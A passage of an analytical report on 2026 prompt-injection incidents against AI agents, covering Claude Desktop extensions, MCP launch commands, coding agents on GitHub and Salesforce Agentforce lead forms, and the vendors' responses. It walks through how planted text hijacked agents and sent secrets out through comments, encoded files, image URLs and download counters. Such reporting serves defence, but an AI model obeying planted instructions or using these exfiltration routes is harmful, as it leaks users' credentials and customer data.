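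The AI Incident Database lists Anthropic as the alleged developer of the system and Cline as both a deployer and a victim. It is fair to call Cline a victim, since it lost control of its own release channel, but the people who installed version 2.3.0 had no part in any of these decisions. They needed someone to make sure that a stranger could not change the software they installed by opening an issue. Only Cline could have promised that, and it would first have needed to understand Anthropic's component, GitHub's cache and the token rules of three registries.

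## Claude Desktop Extensions and the protocol beneath them, February to April 2026

Anthropic's documentation had at least marked Cline's setting as risky. On February 9, 2026, eight days before the altered Cline release, the security company LayerX described how people could end up with a similar agent on their own computers by installing two tools that each worked as intended. Anthropic declined to change its product because users had chosen the tools and granted the permissions. In April, OX Security reported that Anthropic had also declined to change how the official MCP software starts programs, this time leaving the responsibility with developers.

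### A calendar entry that could start a program

Claude Desktop Extensions are MCP servers packaged as single files, which users install with a click and run on their own computers. LayerX's *Claude Desktop Extensions Exposes Over 10,000 Users to Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* describes an attack that needs both Desktop Commander, which runs commands on the computer, and a connector that reads Google Calendar.

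LayerX, which sells browser security, created a calendar event titled "Task Management" with instructions to download code from a public repository and run its build file. The researchers asked Claude to check their latest events "and then take care of it for me." Claude read the event, treated the instructions as the task, and carried them out with Desktop Commander. An attacker who got such an event into someone's calendar, for instance by sending an invitation, could run code of their choice on that person's computer.

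LayerX did not hide or disguise the instructions. The user had asked Claude to deal with whatever was in the calendar, so following the instructions in the event was a plausible reading of the request. That makes this attack harder to train against than most. LayerX did not name the model it tested, but even a model trained to resist planted text can't simply ignore a calendar that its user has told it to act on.

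Browser extensions run in a sandbox, a restricted environment that keeps them away from the rest of the computer. LayerX found that Claude's extensions had no sandbox and ran with "full system privileges". Geordie AI's *Claude Desktop Extensions RCE Vulnerability* explains more precisely that they have the same permissions as the person running Claude Desktop, which is still enough to open that person's documents and steal saved passwords. Roy Paz, the LayerX researcher behind the report, argued in The Register's *Claude add-on turns Google Calendar into malware courier* that nobody can sandbox software that is supposed to have full access. The missing sandbox is therefore a stronger complaint about extensions in general than about Desktop Commander, which people install so that Claude can run commands on their real computer.

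### The score of 10

LayerX gave the flaw the maximum CVSS score of 10. Paz told Infosecurity Magazine that he had set the score himself, using versions 3.0 and 4.0 of the standard (*New Zero-Click Flaw in Claude Desktop Extensions, Anthropic Declines Fix*). The flaw has no CVE, according to the security news site BeyondMachines.

Geordie AI, which sells software for governing AI agents, put the score between 7.6 and 8.0. It compared the flaw with Log4Shell, a 2021 flaw in widely used logging software that did score 10. An attacker could exploit Log4Shell just by sending a request to a vulnerable server. The Claude Desktop attack works only if the victim has turned on the calendar connector, which is off by default, installed a tool that runs commands, granted permissions to both, and asked Claude to act on the calendar. These conditions make the lower score more convincing. LayerX's "zero-click"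 is accurate in that the victim clicks nothing after making the request, but the attacker has to wait for a suitable request from someone with a suitable setup. LayerX said the flaw affected more than 10,000 users but did not report how many of them had both tools.

The flaw does have a public record outside the CVE system. *Zero-Click RCE Vulnerability in Claude Desktop Extensions Exposes 10,000+ Users* (2026), an AI-generated entry in the OECD's incident monitor, repeats LayerX's user count and its description of the flaw as critical.

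Other flaws in Claude Desktop's connectors were easier to classify. BeyondMachines describes how a malicious web page could make Claude pass a crafted address to its Chrome connector, which inserted the address into a command without checking it. The iMessage and Apple Notes connectors had related flaws. In all three, the flaws were in versions before 0.1.9 and came from faulty code that a developer could correct. In LayerX's attack, the calendar connector correctly returned an event and Desktop Commander correctly ran a command, so neither had faulty code to fix.

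### What the user agreed to

Anthropic told LayerX that the flaw "falls outside our current threat model", meaning the set of attacks it designs the product to withstand. It described MCP in Claude Desktop as a "local development tool" whose users choose which servers to run and what to permit. CSO Online's *Anthropic’s DXT poses “critical RCE vulnerability” by running with full system privileges* (2026) quotes Anthropic spokesperson Jennifer Martinez as saying that "the security boundary is defined by the user's configuration choices" and by the computer's existing controls. She added that the attack works only on someone who has intentionally installed these tools and "granted permission to run them without prompts."

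The Decoder's *AI agents face an uncomfortable truth* gives a further reason, based on LayerX's account of Anthropic's thinking: the company wanted extensions to cooperate with as much autonomy as possible. Anthropic does not give this reason in its quoted statements.

Claude Desktop asks before each tool call by default, though the GitHub case showed why people turn that off. LayerX reported that no confirmation appeared in its test but didn't describe the permission settings. If Martinez is right, the user had already told Claude to run commands without asking, which is risky whatever the calendar contains. That would also weaken a comparison Paz made in CSO Online. He said that Microsoft's Copilot, OpenAI's Atlas and Perplexity's Comet ask permission before going beyond the user's instructions, while Claude does not. The comparison is fair only if he left all four products on their default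 settings, and he didn't say whether he had.

Even so, the user had agreed to less than Anthropic's reply implies. Anthropic's *Build a desktop extension with MCPB* describes an installation screen where the user reviews one extension's details and permissions before approving them. The calendar connector needs a separate sign-in with Google. After completing both, a user knows that Claude can read the calendar and run commands. Those steps, as Anthropic describes them, don't explain that people who send calendar invitations may now be able to run commands too. The user would need to know about indirect prompt injection to work that out.

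Anthropic advised users to be as careful with MCP servers as with other third-party software. This advice has the same gap as its warning about malicious servers, which didn't cover the GitHub attack. Even if Desktop Commander is trustworthy and well made, an attacker could still use a calendar event to take control of its user's computer.

Geordie AI gives the best case for Anthropic. Claude Desktop can't run code when first installed, and users must deliberately add a tool that can, much as they would install Docker or an extension for a code editor. Geordie AI argued that any fix would have to solve prompt injection, break legitimate work by separating the tools' privileges, or stop Claude from combining tools, which is much of the reason for using it. Roy Ben Alta, chief executive of the AI vendor Oakie.ai, similarly told CSO Online that the purpose of an agent is to chain actions.

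A smaller change was also possible. Rock Lambros, chief executive of the security firm RockCyber, said a confirmation step was missing between a harmless data source and a tool that runs commands. For example, Claude Desktop could override "always allow" for such tools once a session has read text from outside, using labels like those Microsoft and GitHub later developed. The user would see an extra prompt only in sessions where a stranger might have written the command. Lambros also pointed out that Anthropic had already built sandboxing for its coding agent, Claude Code, so it could hardly present the risk as unavoidable in agents. Paz expected a proper fix to require a full redesign and take weeks, but a confirmation step should need less.

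### Tools for "everyone"

The phrase "local development tool" doesn't match how Anthropic introduced the extensions. The company wrote in its launch post that MCP servers had been largely out of reach for non-technical people, who had to install programming software and edit configuration files by hand. It said extensions would make the servers "accessible to everyone—not just developers." People could install extensions from a curated directory built into Claude Desktop, with "no searching GitHub or vetting code", and Anthropic told developers who submitted extensions that "Our team reviews for quality and security."

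Telling customers that they needn't vet the code is hard to reconcile with later telling them to treat it like any other third-party software. The reviews may have been thorough, but reviewing extensions one at a time would not reveal this problem, since LayerX found no fault in either tool on its own. In a separate advisory, Geordie AI warned that people may assume extensions in a marketplace have been vetted more than they have, and that one-click installation makes it easy to accumulate extensions without a security review.

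The launch post listed several safeguards. The computer's password store would protect sensitive settings, extensions would update themselves, and users could see what they had installed. Companies could block particular extensions or turn off the directory. A company that blocked Desktop Commander would have stopped LayerX's attack, but none of the safeguards dealt with combinations of tools. The Register reported that Anthropic marketed the extensions as sandboxed, though the launch post does not describe them that way.

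Anthropic's defense is reasonable for a programmer who installs a tool for running commands and then switches off the prompts. It is much weaker for the non-technical customers Anthropic was trying to attract. Anthropic trained the model, built the application, designed the extension format and ran the directory, whereas in the Cline case several companies controlled different parts of the system. No user was in a better position than Anthropic to notice that a calendar connector and a command runner were dangerous together. Geordie AI, though sympathetic to Anthropic, also thought users needed better help seeing which combinations create risk.

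### What has changed since February

Anthropic does not appear to have fixed the flaw. As of December 2026, it still compares installing an extension to installing a browser extension on its help page, and invites people to choose from "Anthropic-reviewed tools". The page doesn't mention a sandbox or the risk of combining tools.

By July 2026, Anthropic was calling extensions the "secondary distribution path" in its developer documentation and recommending remote MCP servers, which run on the supplier's computers, for its directory. This may reduce the number of extensions that can act on people's own machines. But Anthropic doesn't describe the change as a security measure in the documentation, and it still recommends extensions for work that needs local files or control of other desktop programs.

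Users can usually choose to always allow a tool, require approval each time, or block it, according to *Claude Desktop*, an independent guide. Anthropic's *MCP, plugins, skills, and hooks*, from November 2026, describes an edition of Claude Desktop that administrators configure centrally. For servers they supply, administrators can lock each tool to "allow", "ask" or "blocked". Locking a command-running tool to "ask" would restore the approval prompt that was missing from LayerX's test. Owners of Anthropic's business plans can also limit which extensions employees install, a control that predates LayerX's report.

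Like "Always Allow" in the GitHub case, these settings don't depend on what the agent has just read, so "ask" also interrupts harmless commands. Someone using Claude Desktop at home can turn "ask" off because there is no administrator to prevent it.

### The command in the configuration file

LayerX's attack needed a tool for running commands. OX Security, which sells software for finding flaws in code, examined an earlier step, when an application starts an MCP server.

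When the server is on the same computer, the application launches it as a program and exchanges messages with it through the program's standard input and output, a method known as stdio. A configuration entry names the program to launch. Cantina, a company that sells security audits, reproduces an example from the documentation of LangChain, a popular framework for building AI applications:

```json
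{
  "command": "python",
  "args": ["/path/to/math_server.py"],
  "transport": "stdio"
}
```

This entry starts a small server that does arithmetic. Developers usually pass such entries to one of the official libraries for building MCP applications. Cantina's excerpts from the Python and TypeScript versions show that these libraries run whatever command the entry contains. If the program isn't an MCP server, the connection fails, but only after the program has run, as flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report* points out.

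This design for executing commands is not itself a prompt injection. An attacker can exploit it without a language model if a product lets strangers write the configuration entry. OX Security's *Anthropic design choice Exposes 150M+ Downloads and up to 200K Servers* describes several products that allowed this through their web interfaces, some without requiring a login.

Prompt injection becomes relevant in coding tools, where planted text can make an agent add an entry to its own configuration file. The tool then launches the program that the entry names. OX reported that in Windsurf, an AI code editor, the attack needed no action from the user. Cantina describes a similar flaw in the rival editor Cursor, whose maker responded by stopping the agent from changing such files without approval.

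OX ran commands on six live commercial platforms and got a harmless test package into nine of the eleven MCP registries it tried. Those results are more informative than its largest numbers. The 150 million downloads in its report's title count copies of software, including copies in products that never give outsiders access to the configuration. The 200,000 servers are an upper estimate, and OX found just over 7,000 that were publicly reachable.

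OX's report lists ten affected products with CVEs, and two of the products share a CVE number. At publication, three products had a patch, one had added a warning, and the other six, including Windsurf, had the status "Reported". None of the listed CVEs is for the MCP kits, so the maintainers of each product had to deal separately with a weakness that OX traced to a single design.

### "Expected" behavior

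OX repeatedly asked Anthropic to change the design. OX's report quotes only one word of Anthropic's answer, "expected". The flyingpenguin post dates OX's first contact to January 7, 2026 and quotes more of the answer. Its author promotes a competing way to run MCP servers. In the reply it quotes, Anthropic called the behavior an explicit part of how stdio servers work and said, "we believe that this design does represent a secure default."

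OX also says that Anthropic made developers responsible for sanitizing input (removing anything dangerous before use). That may be a fair inference, but it isn't in Anthropic's quoted words. LangChain did say this in its quoted reply. FastMCP, which makes another kit for building servers, said that its software starts a program because the MCP specification requires it to. Google acknowledged the issue in its command-line agent but planned no near-term fix.

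Anthropic did change its documentation after OX's first report. According to flyingpenguin, the company's security notes now recommend using stdio adapters "with caution".

A software developer commenting under Tom's Hardware's *Anthropic's Model Context Protocol includes a critical remote code execution vulnerability* made a good case for Anthropic. An application can't start a local server without running a program. If Anthropic restricted the launch command, the maker of a malicious server could move the harmful code into the server itself, which the user would run anyway. The commenter thought registries should keep malicious servers out and application developers should secure their own products. A July 2026 version of Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy* takes a similar position on malicious servers. It also warns that "The SDK's stdio transport is not a sandbox" and makes whoever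 runs a server with reduced privileges responsible for enforcing the isolation.

That argument works well for malicious servers but less well for the web interfaces, where the attacker is a visitor who should never have been able to choose a program. The product's developer is mainly at fault for allowing it, but so many developers made the same mistake that the kits probably made it too easy. The MCP project also knew about the danger. Cantina quotes notes from a maintainers' meeting on March 31, 2026, that read "STDIO = arbitrary local binary execution," and the project's guidance requires applications with one-click installation to show the exact command, identify it as potentially dangerous and get the user's explicit approval.

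The one-click requirement covers people installing servers on their own computers, but it does not help operators of public websites, where the person approving the command may be the attacker.

### OX's proposed fixes

OX proposed four changes, and according to flyingpenguin, Anthropic declined all of them:

- The kits would launch only servers described in a manifest, a fixed description of the server, instead of accepting any command.
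- The kits would accept only approved commands and block high-risk programs by default.
- Developers would have to turn on a "dangerous mode" before building a launch command from changeable input.
- Registries would require security manifests signed by developers whose identity had been verified.

OX's own research is evidence against the list of approved commands. Flowise, a tool for building AI applications, already allowed only certain commands and removed special characters. OX bypassed those checks in one step by using an option of an approved program. The flyingpenguin post treats this as proof that application developers can't be expected to solve the problem. But a similar list inside the official kits could fail in the same way, because programs that download and run other software are a common way to start MCP servers.

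Signed manifests would make it easier to trace a malicious server to its maker, but they wouldn't prevent a verified developer from publishing one. Launching servers only from a manifest would protect a web product as long as visitors couldn't supply the manifest.

The "dangerous mode" seems the most useful of the four. A developer could still expose the command to strangers, but would first have to switch on an option with an alarming name. Developers who always launch the same server would notice no difference. Some existing products would stop working until their developers made the change, and OX's claim that a fix in the kits would protect everyone "instantly" is too strong, since each product would first have to adopt the new version. Still, the change would have taken Anthropic little effort, and in its quoted reply the company doesn't explain why a default that accepts any command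 is more secure than one that asks developers to opt in.

### The move to the Linux Foundation

When OX contacted Anthropic, the company had already donated MCP to the Agentic AI Foundation, a new body within the Linux Foundation, a nonprofit that hosts open-source projects. Anthropic announced the donation on December 9, 2025, and someone who read only that announcement might conclude that OX had written to the wrong organization.

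In practice, the same people still made the decisions. "For MCP little changes," Model Context Protocol (2025) wrote in its announcement. The foundation's board controls budgets, membership and the admission of new projects, while MCP's existing maintainers keep full control of its technical direction. Tom's Hardware reported in April that Anthropic was still responsible for maintaining the official kits. In its reply to OX, as quoted, Anthropic defended the design and didn't refer OX to the foundation.

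Anthropic therefore can't use the donation to disclaim responsibility for the kits, and it doesn't seem to have tried. But the protocol has a public process for proposing changes, and a Security Interest Group that vets reported threats and passes them to the relevant maintainers. OX's report mentions requests to Anthropic but no proposal through that process. A formal proposal for the "dangerous mode" might at least get the maintainers to explain publicly why they accepted or rejected it.

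## One attack on three vendors' coding agents, October 2025 to August 2026

On April 15, 2026, the security engineer Aonan Guan published an attack that worked on coding agents made by Anthropic, Google and GitHub. Working with Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University, he had used one method to take secret keys from all three companies' agents. We can compare how the vendors responded to this attack, unlike the calendar attack, which LayerX reported only to Anthropic. All three companies paid a bounty, and none had published a security advisory when Guan's account came out.

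Guan called the attack "Comment and Control", after command and control, the usual term for the servers through which attackers direct hijacked machines. The attacker needs no such server here, because the instructions reach the agent as ordinary project text on GitHub, and the attacker collects the stolen keys from a comment, a log entry or a file on the same site.

### How the keys left through GitHub

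Claude Code Security Review is an Anthropic component for GitHub Actions that uses Claude to check pull requests for security flaws. The outsider controlled a pull request's title, and the component copied that title straight into the prompt. ThreatCluster's *Comment And Control Prompt Injection Credential Theft* (2026), a repost of Guan's own account, describes a title containing an instruction for Claude to list the programs running on the machine and their environment variables. Environment variables are named settings that a program receives when it starts, and build pipelines commonly use them to pass secret keys.

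Anthropic had not restricted which tools the agent could use, and the agent's process inherited every variable in the job. Claude reported the list as a "security finding", and the component posted it as a comment on the pull request. The comment contained the project's key for Anthropic's models and a GitHub token. The same output went into the job's log, where an attacker could collect it without leaving a trace in the conversation.

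Google's Gemini CLI Action runs Gemini on a project's issues. The outsider controlled the issue's title, body and comments. The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties* reports that Guan overrode Gemini's safety instructions by adding a fake "trusted content section" after the genuine text. Gemini then posted its own API key as a public comment.

GitHub's Copilot Agent, which writes code and opens pull requests, was harder to attack. It starts work on an issue only when someone assigns it, so Guan needed an issue that would look harmless to that person. He put the instructions in an HTML comment. GitHub doesn't display such comments, but most agents receive the raw text, as *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (2026) points out. The person assigning the issue saw only a short request for debugging.

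GitHub had also built three protections around Copilot that the other two agents lacked, and Guan got past all of them:

- A filter removed secret variables from the commands that Copilot ran. It did not remove them from the program that launched those commands or from the MCP server running beside it, and a command could read the variables of both.
- A scanner checked Copilot's changes for secrets before uploading them. It recognized GitHub's tokens by their opening characters, so Guan had Copilot encode the output first.
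- A firewall allowed connections only to approved sites. GitHub had to be one of them, because the agent's job is to upload code there.

Copilot added the encoded file to a pull request, where the attacker could download it and recover four credentials. The firewall had the same weakness as OpenAI's url_safe check, because it approved a domain where outsiders could read the data sent to it.

These were researchers' demonstrations. The Next Web says such flaws have already been exploited in real attacks, which is consistent with the Cline theft, but no account names a victim of these three attacks. Unlike the other two, the attack on Anthropic's component depends on a project's settings. OODA Loop's *Three AI coding agents leaked secrets through a single prompt injection* notes that GitHub by default withholds secrets from jobs that run on pull requests from forks, the separate copies in which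 outsiders normally work. A stranger could get the secrets only from a project that had overridden this default, and Guan says such projects exist. Jobs that start when someone files an issue have no equivalent protection, so Gemini's users were more exposed to strangers.

### Three replies to one method

| | Anthropic | Google | GitHub |
|---|---|---|---|
| Assessment | Critical, CVSS 9.4 | Accepted the report | "Known issue", later an architectural limitation |
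| Bounty | $100 | $1,337 | $500 |
| Known change to the software | Blocked one command | Added instructions to the system prompt | None |
| CVE or advisory at publication | None | None | None |

Anthropic was the first of the three vendors to learn of the attack, in October 2025. According to The Next Web, Anthropic asked whether the method could also take GitHub tokens. After learning that it could, the company raised the attack's severity score from 9.3 to 9.4, and it paid in November. It told Guan that the component "is not designed to be hardened against prompt injection" and added a warning to the documentation. On the page for *Claude Code Security Review*, Anthropic now tells people to use the tool only on "trusted PRs" and to require a maintainer's approval before it runs on an outsider's work.

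That warning is clear, and a project whose own staff write all the code can follow it without losing much. But it is an awkward limit for a security review tool, because maintainers have the most reason to want a security check when code comes from strangers, and Anthropic advises against running the tool unattended on that code.

Anthropic's code change only blocked ps, the command that lists running programs, and left the agent's other tools in place. Guan pointed out that the same information was available by another route. SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection* reports that, according to Guan, the attack still worked in principle with a revised payload, though he had not attempted a full bypass after the fix. Google left Gemini's tools unchanged and added "guardrail prompts", which ask the model to behave safely. This was in one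 respect even weaker than Anthropic's change, because Guan had just shown that planted text could override such instructions.

GitHub first closed the report, calling the problem a known issue without significant security risk, and said it could not reproduce it. Guan replied with the filter he had found in Copilot's code. GitHub had written the filter to keep these secrets away from Copilot's commands, so it evidently considered their exposure a risk. GitHub reopened the report and paid in March 2026, but still called the flaw a "previously identified architectural limitation". It said it was exploring ways to restrict access further and thanked Guan for starting "some great internal discussions".

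Anthropic paid the smallest bounty, $100, for a flaw it rated critical, so the bounties don't match the companies' own views of the danger. Bounty size depends partly on what a program covers, so the low payment is poor evidence that Anthropic took the report lightly. Its choice of fix is better evidence of how seriously it took the report. Guan recommended giving each agent only the tools and secrets its job requires. A reviewer that reads code and writes comments can do most of its work without running commands, so Anthropic could have removed that ability with little loss to users.

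GitHub had a harder problem because a coding agent has to run commands to test what it writes. Removing credentials from those commands, though sensible, could not protect them while a command could inspect another program in the same environment that still held them. GitHub would have needed to keep the credentials in a separate environment. Anthropic's later fixes to the component Cline used had a similar problem.

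### Staying on an old version

The Next Web argues that, without a CVE or an advisory, users of older versions may never learn that they are exposed. How much this matters depends on how a project installed the agent. A project can have GitHub Actions fetch a component's newest code at every run, or it can pin the component to one version. Anthropic's sample setup for the security reviewer fetches the newest code, so anyone who copied it received the block on ps automatically. Projects that had pinned an earlier version kept the old code. Pinning is a standard precaution against attackers who take over a component and alter it, so the people who missed the fix were probably among the more careful ones. Copilot's users could not choose a version, because GitHub runs that agent as a service.

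The updates would have helped less than security updates usually do, because they left most of the agents' access in place. Existing users of Anthropic's component had more to gain from the new advice to keep it away from untrusted pull requests, but Anthropic put that advice on a page that people mostly read during installation. An advisory could have reached those who had installed the component months earlier.

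### Flaws that did receive CVEs

On April 24, nine days after Guan's post, Google published an advisory for a different flaw in Gemini CLI. It credited Dan Lisichkin and Elad Meged, according to Snyk's *Command Injection Affecting @google/gemini-cli package* (2026). Meged works for Novee Security, which builds AI agents that test companies' defenses. In August, at the Black Hat security conference in Las Vegas, he presented attacks on coding agents from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI. *Black Hat 2026* (Underhill, 2026) reports that Novee found the flaws in the vendors' own repositories, running their default configurations. The vendors had chosen these settings themselves, which made it harder to blame a customer than it had been in Cline's case.

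The Gemini flaw concerned a folder called .gemini, from which the program loads its settings. A person running Gemini CLI must mark a project's folder as trusted before the program loads those settings. In a build pipeline, nobody is there to do this, so the program trusted the folder automatically. Mondoo's *GHSA-wpqr-6v78-jr5g* reproduces Google's warning about pipelines that review outsiders' pull requests. Without having to fool the model, an attacker could get the program to run their code by including a .gemini folder with malicious settings in the pull request. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-12537* (2026), an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, adds that the code ran before the sandbox started.

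Google changed the default so that pipelines must mark a folder as trusted before Gemini CLI loads its settings. Google accepted that some customers' pipelines would stop loading their settings until somebody updated them. It had been much more cautious with Guan's report on the same product, when it only added text to a prompt and broke nothing. The April advisory also covers a way around the list of permitted tools. OSV's *GHSA-wpqr-6v78-jr5g* (2026) shows a severity score of 10.0.

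Anthropic's case took longer to appear in a public record. Novee had used a planted GitHub issue to run code in Anthropic's pipeline, read files and steal keys for GitHub and for Anthropic's models. Underhill reports that Anthropic issued several patches before a CVE appeared. The advisory, dated June 17 in GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026), describes only one route by which data could leak, which is narrower than the attack Novee demonstrated.

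That route used Hugging Face, a site where anyone can publish AI models. Claude Code normally asks permission before its WebFetch tool opens an unfamiliar address, but Anthropic had already approved all of huggingface.co. The site counts downloads of each model's files. An attacker could publish several models, have a hijacked Claude request their files in a chosen pattern, and read the stolen data from the changing counts. This resembles the alphabet method that researchers used against ChatGPT, with download counters in place of a server log. Users who had limited the agent's tools were also exposed, because the approved domain bypassed that limit.

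Claude Code users with automatic updates already had the fix when the advisory came out, and Anthropic told everyone else to update. OSV's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) lists 2.1.163 as the first safe version and June 23 as the date of the CVE. GitHub assigned that CVE, as it does for many projects hosted on its site. Google assigned its own for the Gemini CLI flaw, CVE-2026-12537, and published it on June 24, according to MITRE's *Unauthenticated Remote Code Execution in Gemini CLI CI/CD Workflows* (2026). Both flaws had public records more than a month before the August talk.

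### What the records reached

Snyk added the Gemini flaw to its scanner database on April 27, when the flaw had an advisory but no CVE. Since an advisory was enough for at least one commercial scanner to warn its customers, the missing advisories for the flaws Guan reported probably mattered more than the missing CVEs.

A CVE still reaches more people than a vendor's advisory does. The UAE's Cyber Security Council issued its alert, *Critical Remote Code Execution Vulnerability in Google Gemini CLI* (2026), on June 29, five days after Google's CVE and two months after the advisory. Red Hat's *CVE-2026-54316* lists one of Red Hat's own products as containing an affected version of Claude Code. Customers of that product might not have known it included Claude Code, so they could easily have missed advice from Anthropic to update it.

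The severity scores were less helpful because they differed between versions of the CVSS standard. NixOS's *NIXPKGS-2026-1974*, a tracker entry for a Linux distribution, rates the Claude Code flaw 6.0 (medium) under version 4.0. Wiz's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) rates it 9.1 (critical) under version 3.1. A company that patches critical flaws at once and leaves medium ones for later would patch this flaw sooner or later depending on which page it read. INCIBE's entry for Gemini CLI also lists two scores, 10.0 under version 4.0 and 7.8 under the older version.

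### Why these flaws and not the earlier ones

Both CVEs describe a rule that the vendor's own code failed to enforce. Claude Code was supposed to ask before opening addresses that strangers control, and Gemini CLI was supposed to load settings only from trusted folders. Each vendor could name the version that began enforcing its rule, and neither had to treat prompt injection as the flaw. Anthropic's record mentions prompt injection only as a precondition, since the attacker first needs a way to get untrusted text in front of Claude. Installing version 2.1.163 closes the route through Hugging Face but otherwise leaves users as open to planted instructions as before.

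Anthropic's reply to Guan avoided making any such rule. If a component "is not designed to be hardened against prompt injection", a successful injection doesn't violate any commitment by the vendor. Google had no specific rule to fix either. Its model was supposed to follow its own instructions but sometimes followed instructions from a stranger.

This explanation doesn't fit Copilot. GitHub had built a filter to keep secrets from the agent's commands, and Guan showed that the filter failed, which is much the same kind of fault as an overly broad approved list. The lack of a version number wasn't a real obstacle either, since EchoLeak received a CVE even though Microsoft runs the affected product as a service. The flaw in Anthropic's component was rated critical, and an identifiable code change marked the fix. The vendors could have published something about all three flaws, even if only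 to say that the fix was partial.

An ordinary coding fault doesn't guarantee a CVE either. Slides published by Black Hat (2026) from its Asian conference count the command-injection flaws that researchers reported in coding agents. These flaws let an attacker slip an extra command past the software's checks. Claude Code had four reports and two CVEs. Gemini CLI had two reports and Amazon's Kiro had four, with no CVE for either. Command injection is among the most familiar kinds of software flaw, so the vendors' habits must explain some of the missing CVEs.

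The OpenAI flaw described in the August research is hard to record. OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, reads standing instructions from a file called AGENTS.md. In OpenAI's own repository, several automated stages shared a workspace, and a planted issue could make the agent write new instructions into that file for the next stage to obey. OpenAI separated the stages and documented the file as untrusted input, and Underhill lists no CVE for the flaw.

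Other projects can make the same mistake even with a fully updated copy of Codex. *Demystifying and Detecting Agentic Workflow Injection Vulnerabilities in GitHub Actions* (2026) examines a related example, adapted from the job that labels issues in OpenAI's repository. The issue's text goes into the prompt beside the maintainers' instructions, and the agent's answer goes into a script that applies the labels. An outsider can therefore try to influence the agent and, through its answer, the script, which doesn't use a model.

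In *GitInject*, Isbarov, Suleymanov and colleagues (2026) ran eleven attacks against real workflows built on four AI providers' agents. Two that used planted configuration files also worked on GitLab and Hugging Face, so the danger isn't limited to GitHub. A scanner that compares version numbers can't find a flaw like the one in OpenAI's repository, because such flaws are in the workflow that each project writes for itself.

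## Business agents that read public web forms, 2025 to September 2026

Business agents, like coding agents that read public bug reports, can receive text from strangers. Sales teams want to hear from people they have never met, so many businesses put a contact form on their website and save each entry in the same database as their existing customers. Salesforce and Microsoft sell platforms for building agents that handle these entries. Between September 2025 and September 2026, three security companies showed that a stranger could extract customer data from Salesforce's agents by filling in such a form. Salesforce changed its platform each time, mostly by blocking a route through which data could leave, but planted text could still hijack the agents.

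### A form that anyone can fill in

Businesses use Salesforce's main product, a customer relationship management (CRM) database, to track customers, deals and "leads" (potential customers). Its Web-to-Lead feature provides a form for a business's public website and turns each submission into a lead record. With Agentforce, businesses can add an AI agent that reads those records, answers employees' questions about them and drafts replies.

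Salesforce and the business using its software split the deployer's role. Salesforce supplies the database, the form, the agent software and the chat window. The business decides whether to switch on the form, what records the agent may read and what actions it may take. The attacker doesn't need an account with either company, whereas the attacker in the Slack AI demonstration had to belong to the victim's workspace.

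### ForcedLeak and the five-dollar domain

Noma Security, which sells protection for AI agents, reported the first of these leaks to Salesforce on July 28, 2025 and named it ForcedLeak. Nytro (2025) copied Noma's full report to a security forum under the title *ForcedLeak*. Noma began by asking an Agentforce agent what color red and yellow make. The agent answered "Orange", so it would deal with requests that had nothing to do with sales. Noma then looked for somewhere to put instructions. The boxes for names, company and email hold 40 or 80 characters, but the Description box holds 42,000. The attack went like this:

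1. The attacker submits the form under the name "Alice Bob", with four numbered requests in the Description box. The third asks for the email addresses of the company's leads. The fourth asks for an image whose web address ends with the answer to the third.
2. An employee asks Agentforce to check Alice Bob's entry, answer the questions in it and draft an email with the results.
3. The agent treats the four requests as part of the job and looks up the addresses.
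4. The chat window loads the image, which sends the addresses to the attacker's server.

The four requests totaled only about 400 characters, so they would have fit in a much shorter text box. Noma also wrote the employee's request, which it called "optimized". Its wording encouraged the agent to follow the planted text, as in LayerX's calendar test. A request for a plain summary might have been harder to exploit.

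The last step should have failed because Salesforce, like Bing Chat, limited images to domains listed in a content security policy. But the registration for one of the more than twenty listed domains, my-salesforce-cms.com, had expired, and Noma bought it for $5. The policy still listed the domain, so the browser loaded images from it. In *ForcedLeak*, Willison called the result a classic case of the lethal trifecta.

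The same policy allowed every address under amazonaws.com, where anyone can rent storage from Amazon. An attacker might therefore not have needed the expired domain, though Noma didn't report trying this. Rehberger used windows.net in a similar way against ChatGPT.

Salesforce acknowledged the report within three days and later took back control of the domain. *Agentforce Web-to-Lead Vulnerability Exposed* (Martin, 2025) reports that Salesforce made a larger change on September 8, more than two weeks before Noma published. Noma gave the flaw a CVSS score of 9.4. Noma's attack was a demonstration, but *Prompt injection* (2025), an article in The Register, reports that Salesforce would not say whether anyone had exploited the flaw.

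### What the trusted list covered

From September 8, an agent could use an outside web address only if the business's administrator had added it to an approved list called Trusted URLs. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* explains that the Agentforce chat window replaces any unapproved address in an answer with a redaction notice. The redaction applies to addresses in images, links and page styling.

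Salesforce told customers that the list would "ensure no malicious links are called or generated", according to The Hacker News (2025). It also described the list as a safeguard for use "after a successful prompt injection", acknowledging that planted text could still take control of the agent. Its promise covered links but not other ways a hijacked agent might send data.

Salesforce could hardly have stopped its agents from reading the Description box, because salespeople need to know what a lead wants. It could have screened the text for instructions, as Microsoft apparently did after an earlier attack on Copilot Studio, Microsoft's platform for building agents. In February 2025, Zenity Labs, the research arm of a company that sells security for AI agents, reported that a planted message could extract data from an agent it had built on the platform. According to Zenity's account, published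 by the Cloud Security Alliance, Microsoft rated the flaw critical and fixed it within two months. Zenity's tests suggested that Microsoft had mainly added a filter that recognized the malicious text, so differently worded instructions might still have worked.

Microsoft changed the platform in that case, even though the business's settings had mattered there too. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* warned customers not to let just anyone trigger an agent, and pointed out that McKinsey had configured a customer service agent to respond to any email.

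Unlike a text filter, an address filter works regardless of how the attacker words the instructions, but it only stops data that leaves in a web address. It also gives administrators more work. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* warns that agents could stop working properly if administrators didn't approve every outside domain they needed. Each approval applies throughout the business's Salesforce system, so the agent can also use domains approved for other purposes. PromptArmor advises against broad approvals that cover sites where outsiders can post material.

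### Copilot Studio and Agentforce in spring 2026

In April 2026, Capsule Security published attacks on Microsoft's and Salesforce's AI agent platforms that sent data out by email. Security Boulevard's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* (2026) describes how each attack began with a form. Claw Times reports that Capsule called the Microsoft flaw ShareLeak and the Salesforce flaw PipeLeak, and also gives the vendors' responses.

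| | ShareLeak, Copilot Studio | PipeLeak, Agentforce |
|---|---|---|
| Where the attacker writes | A form in SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service | A public lead form |
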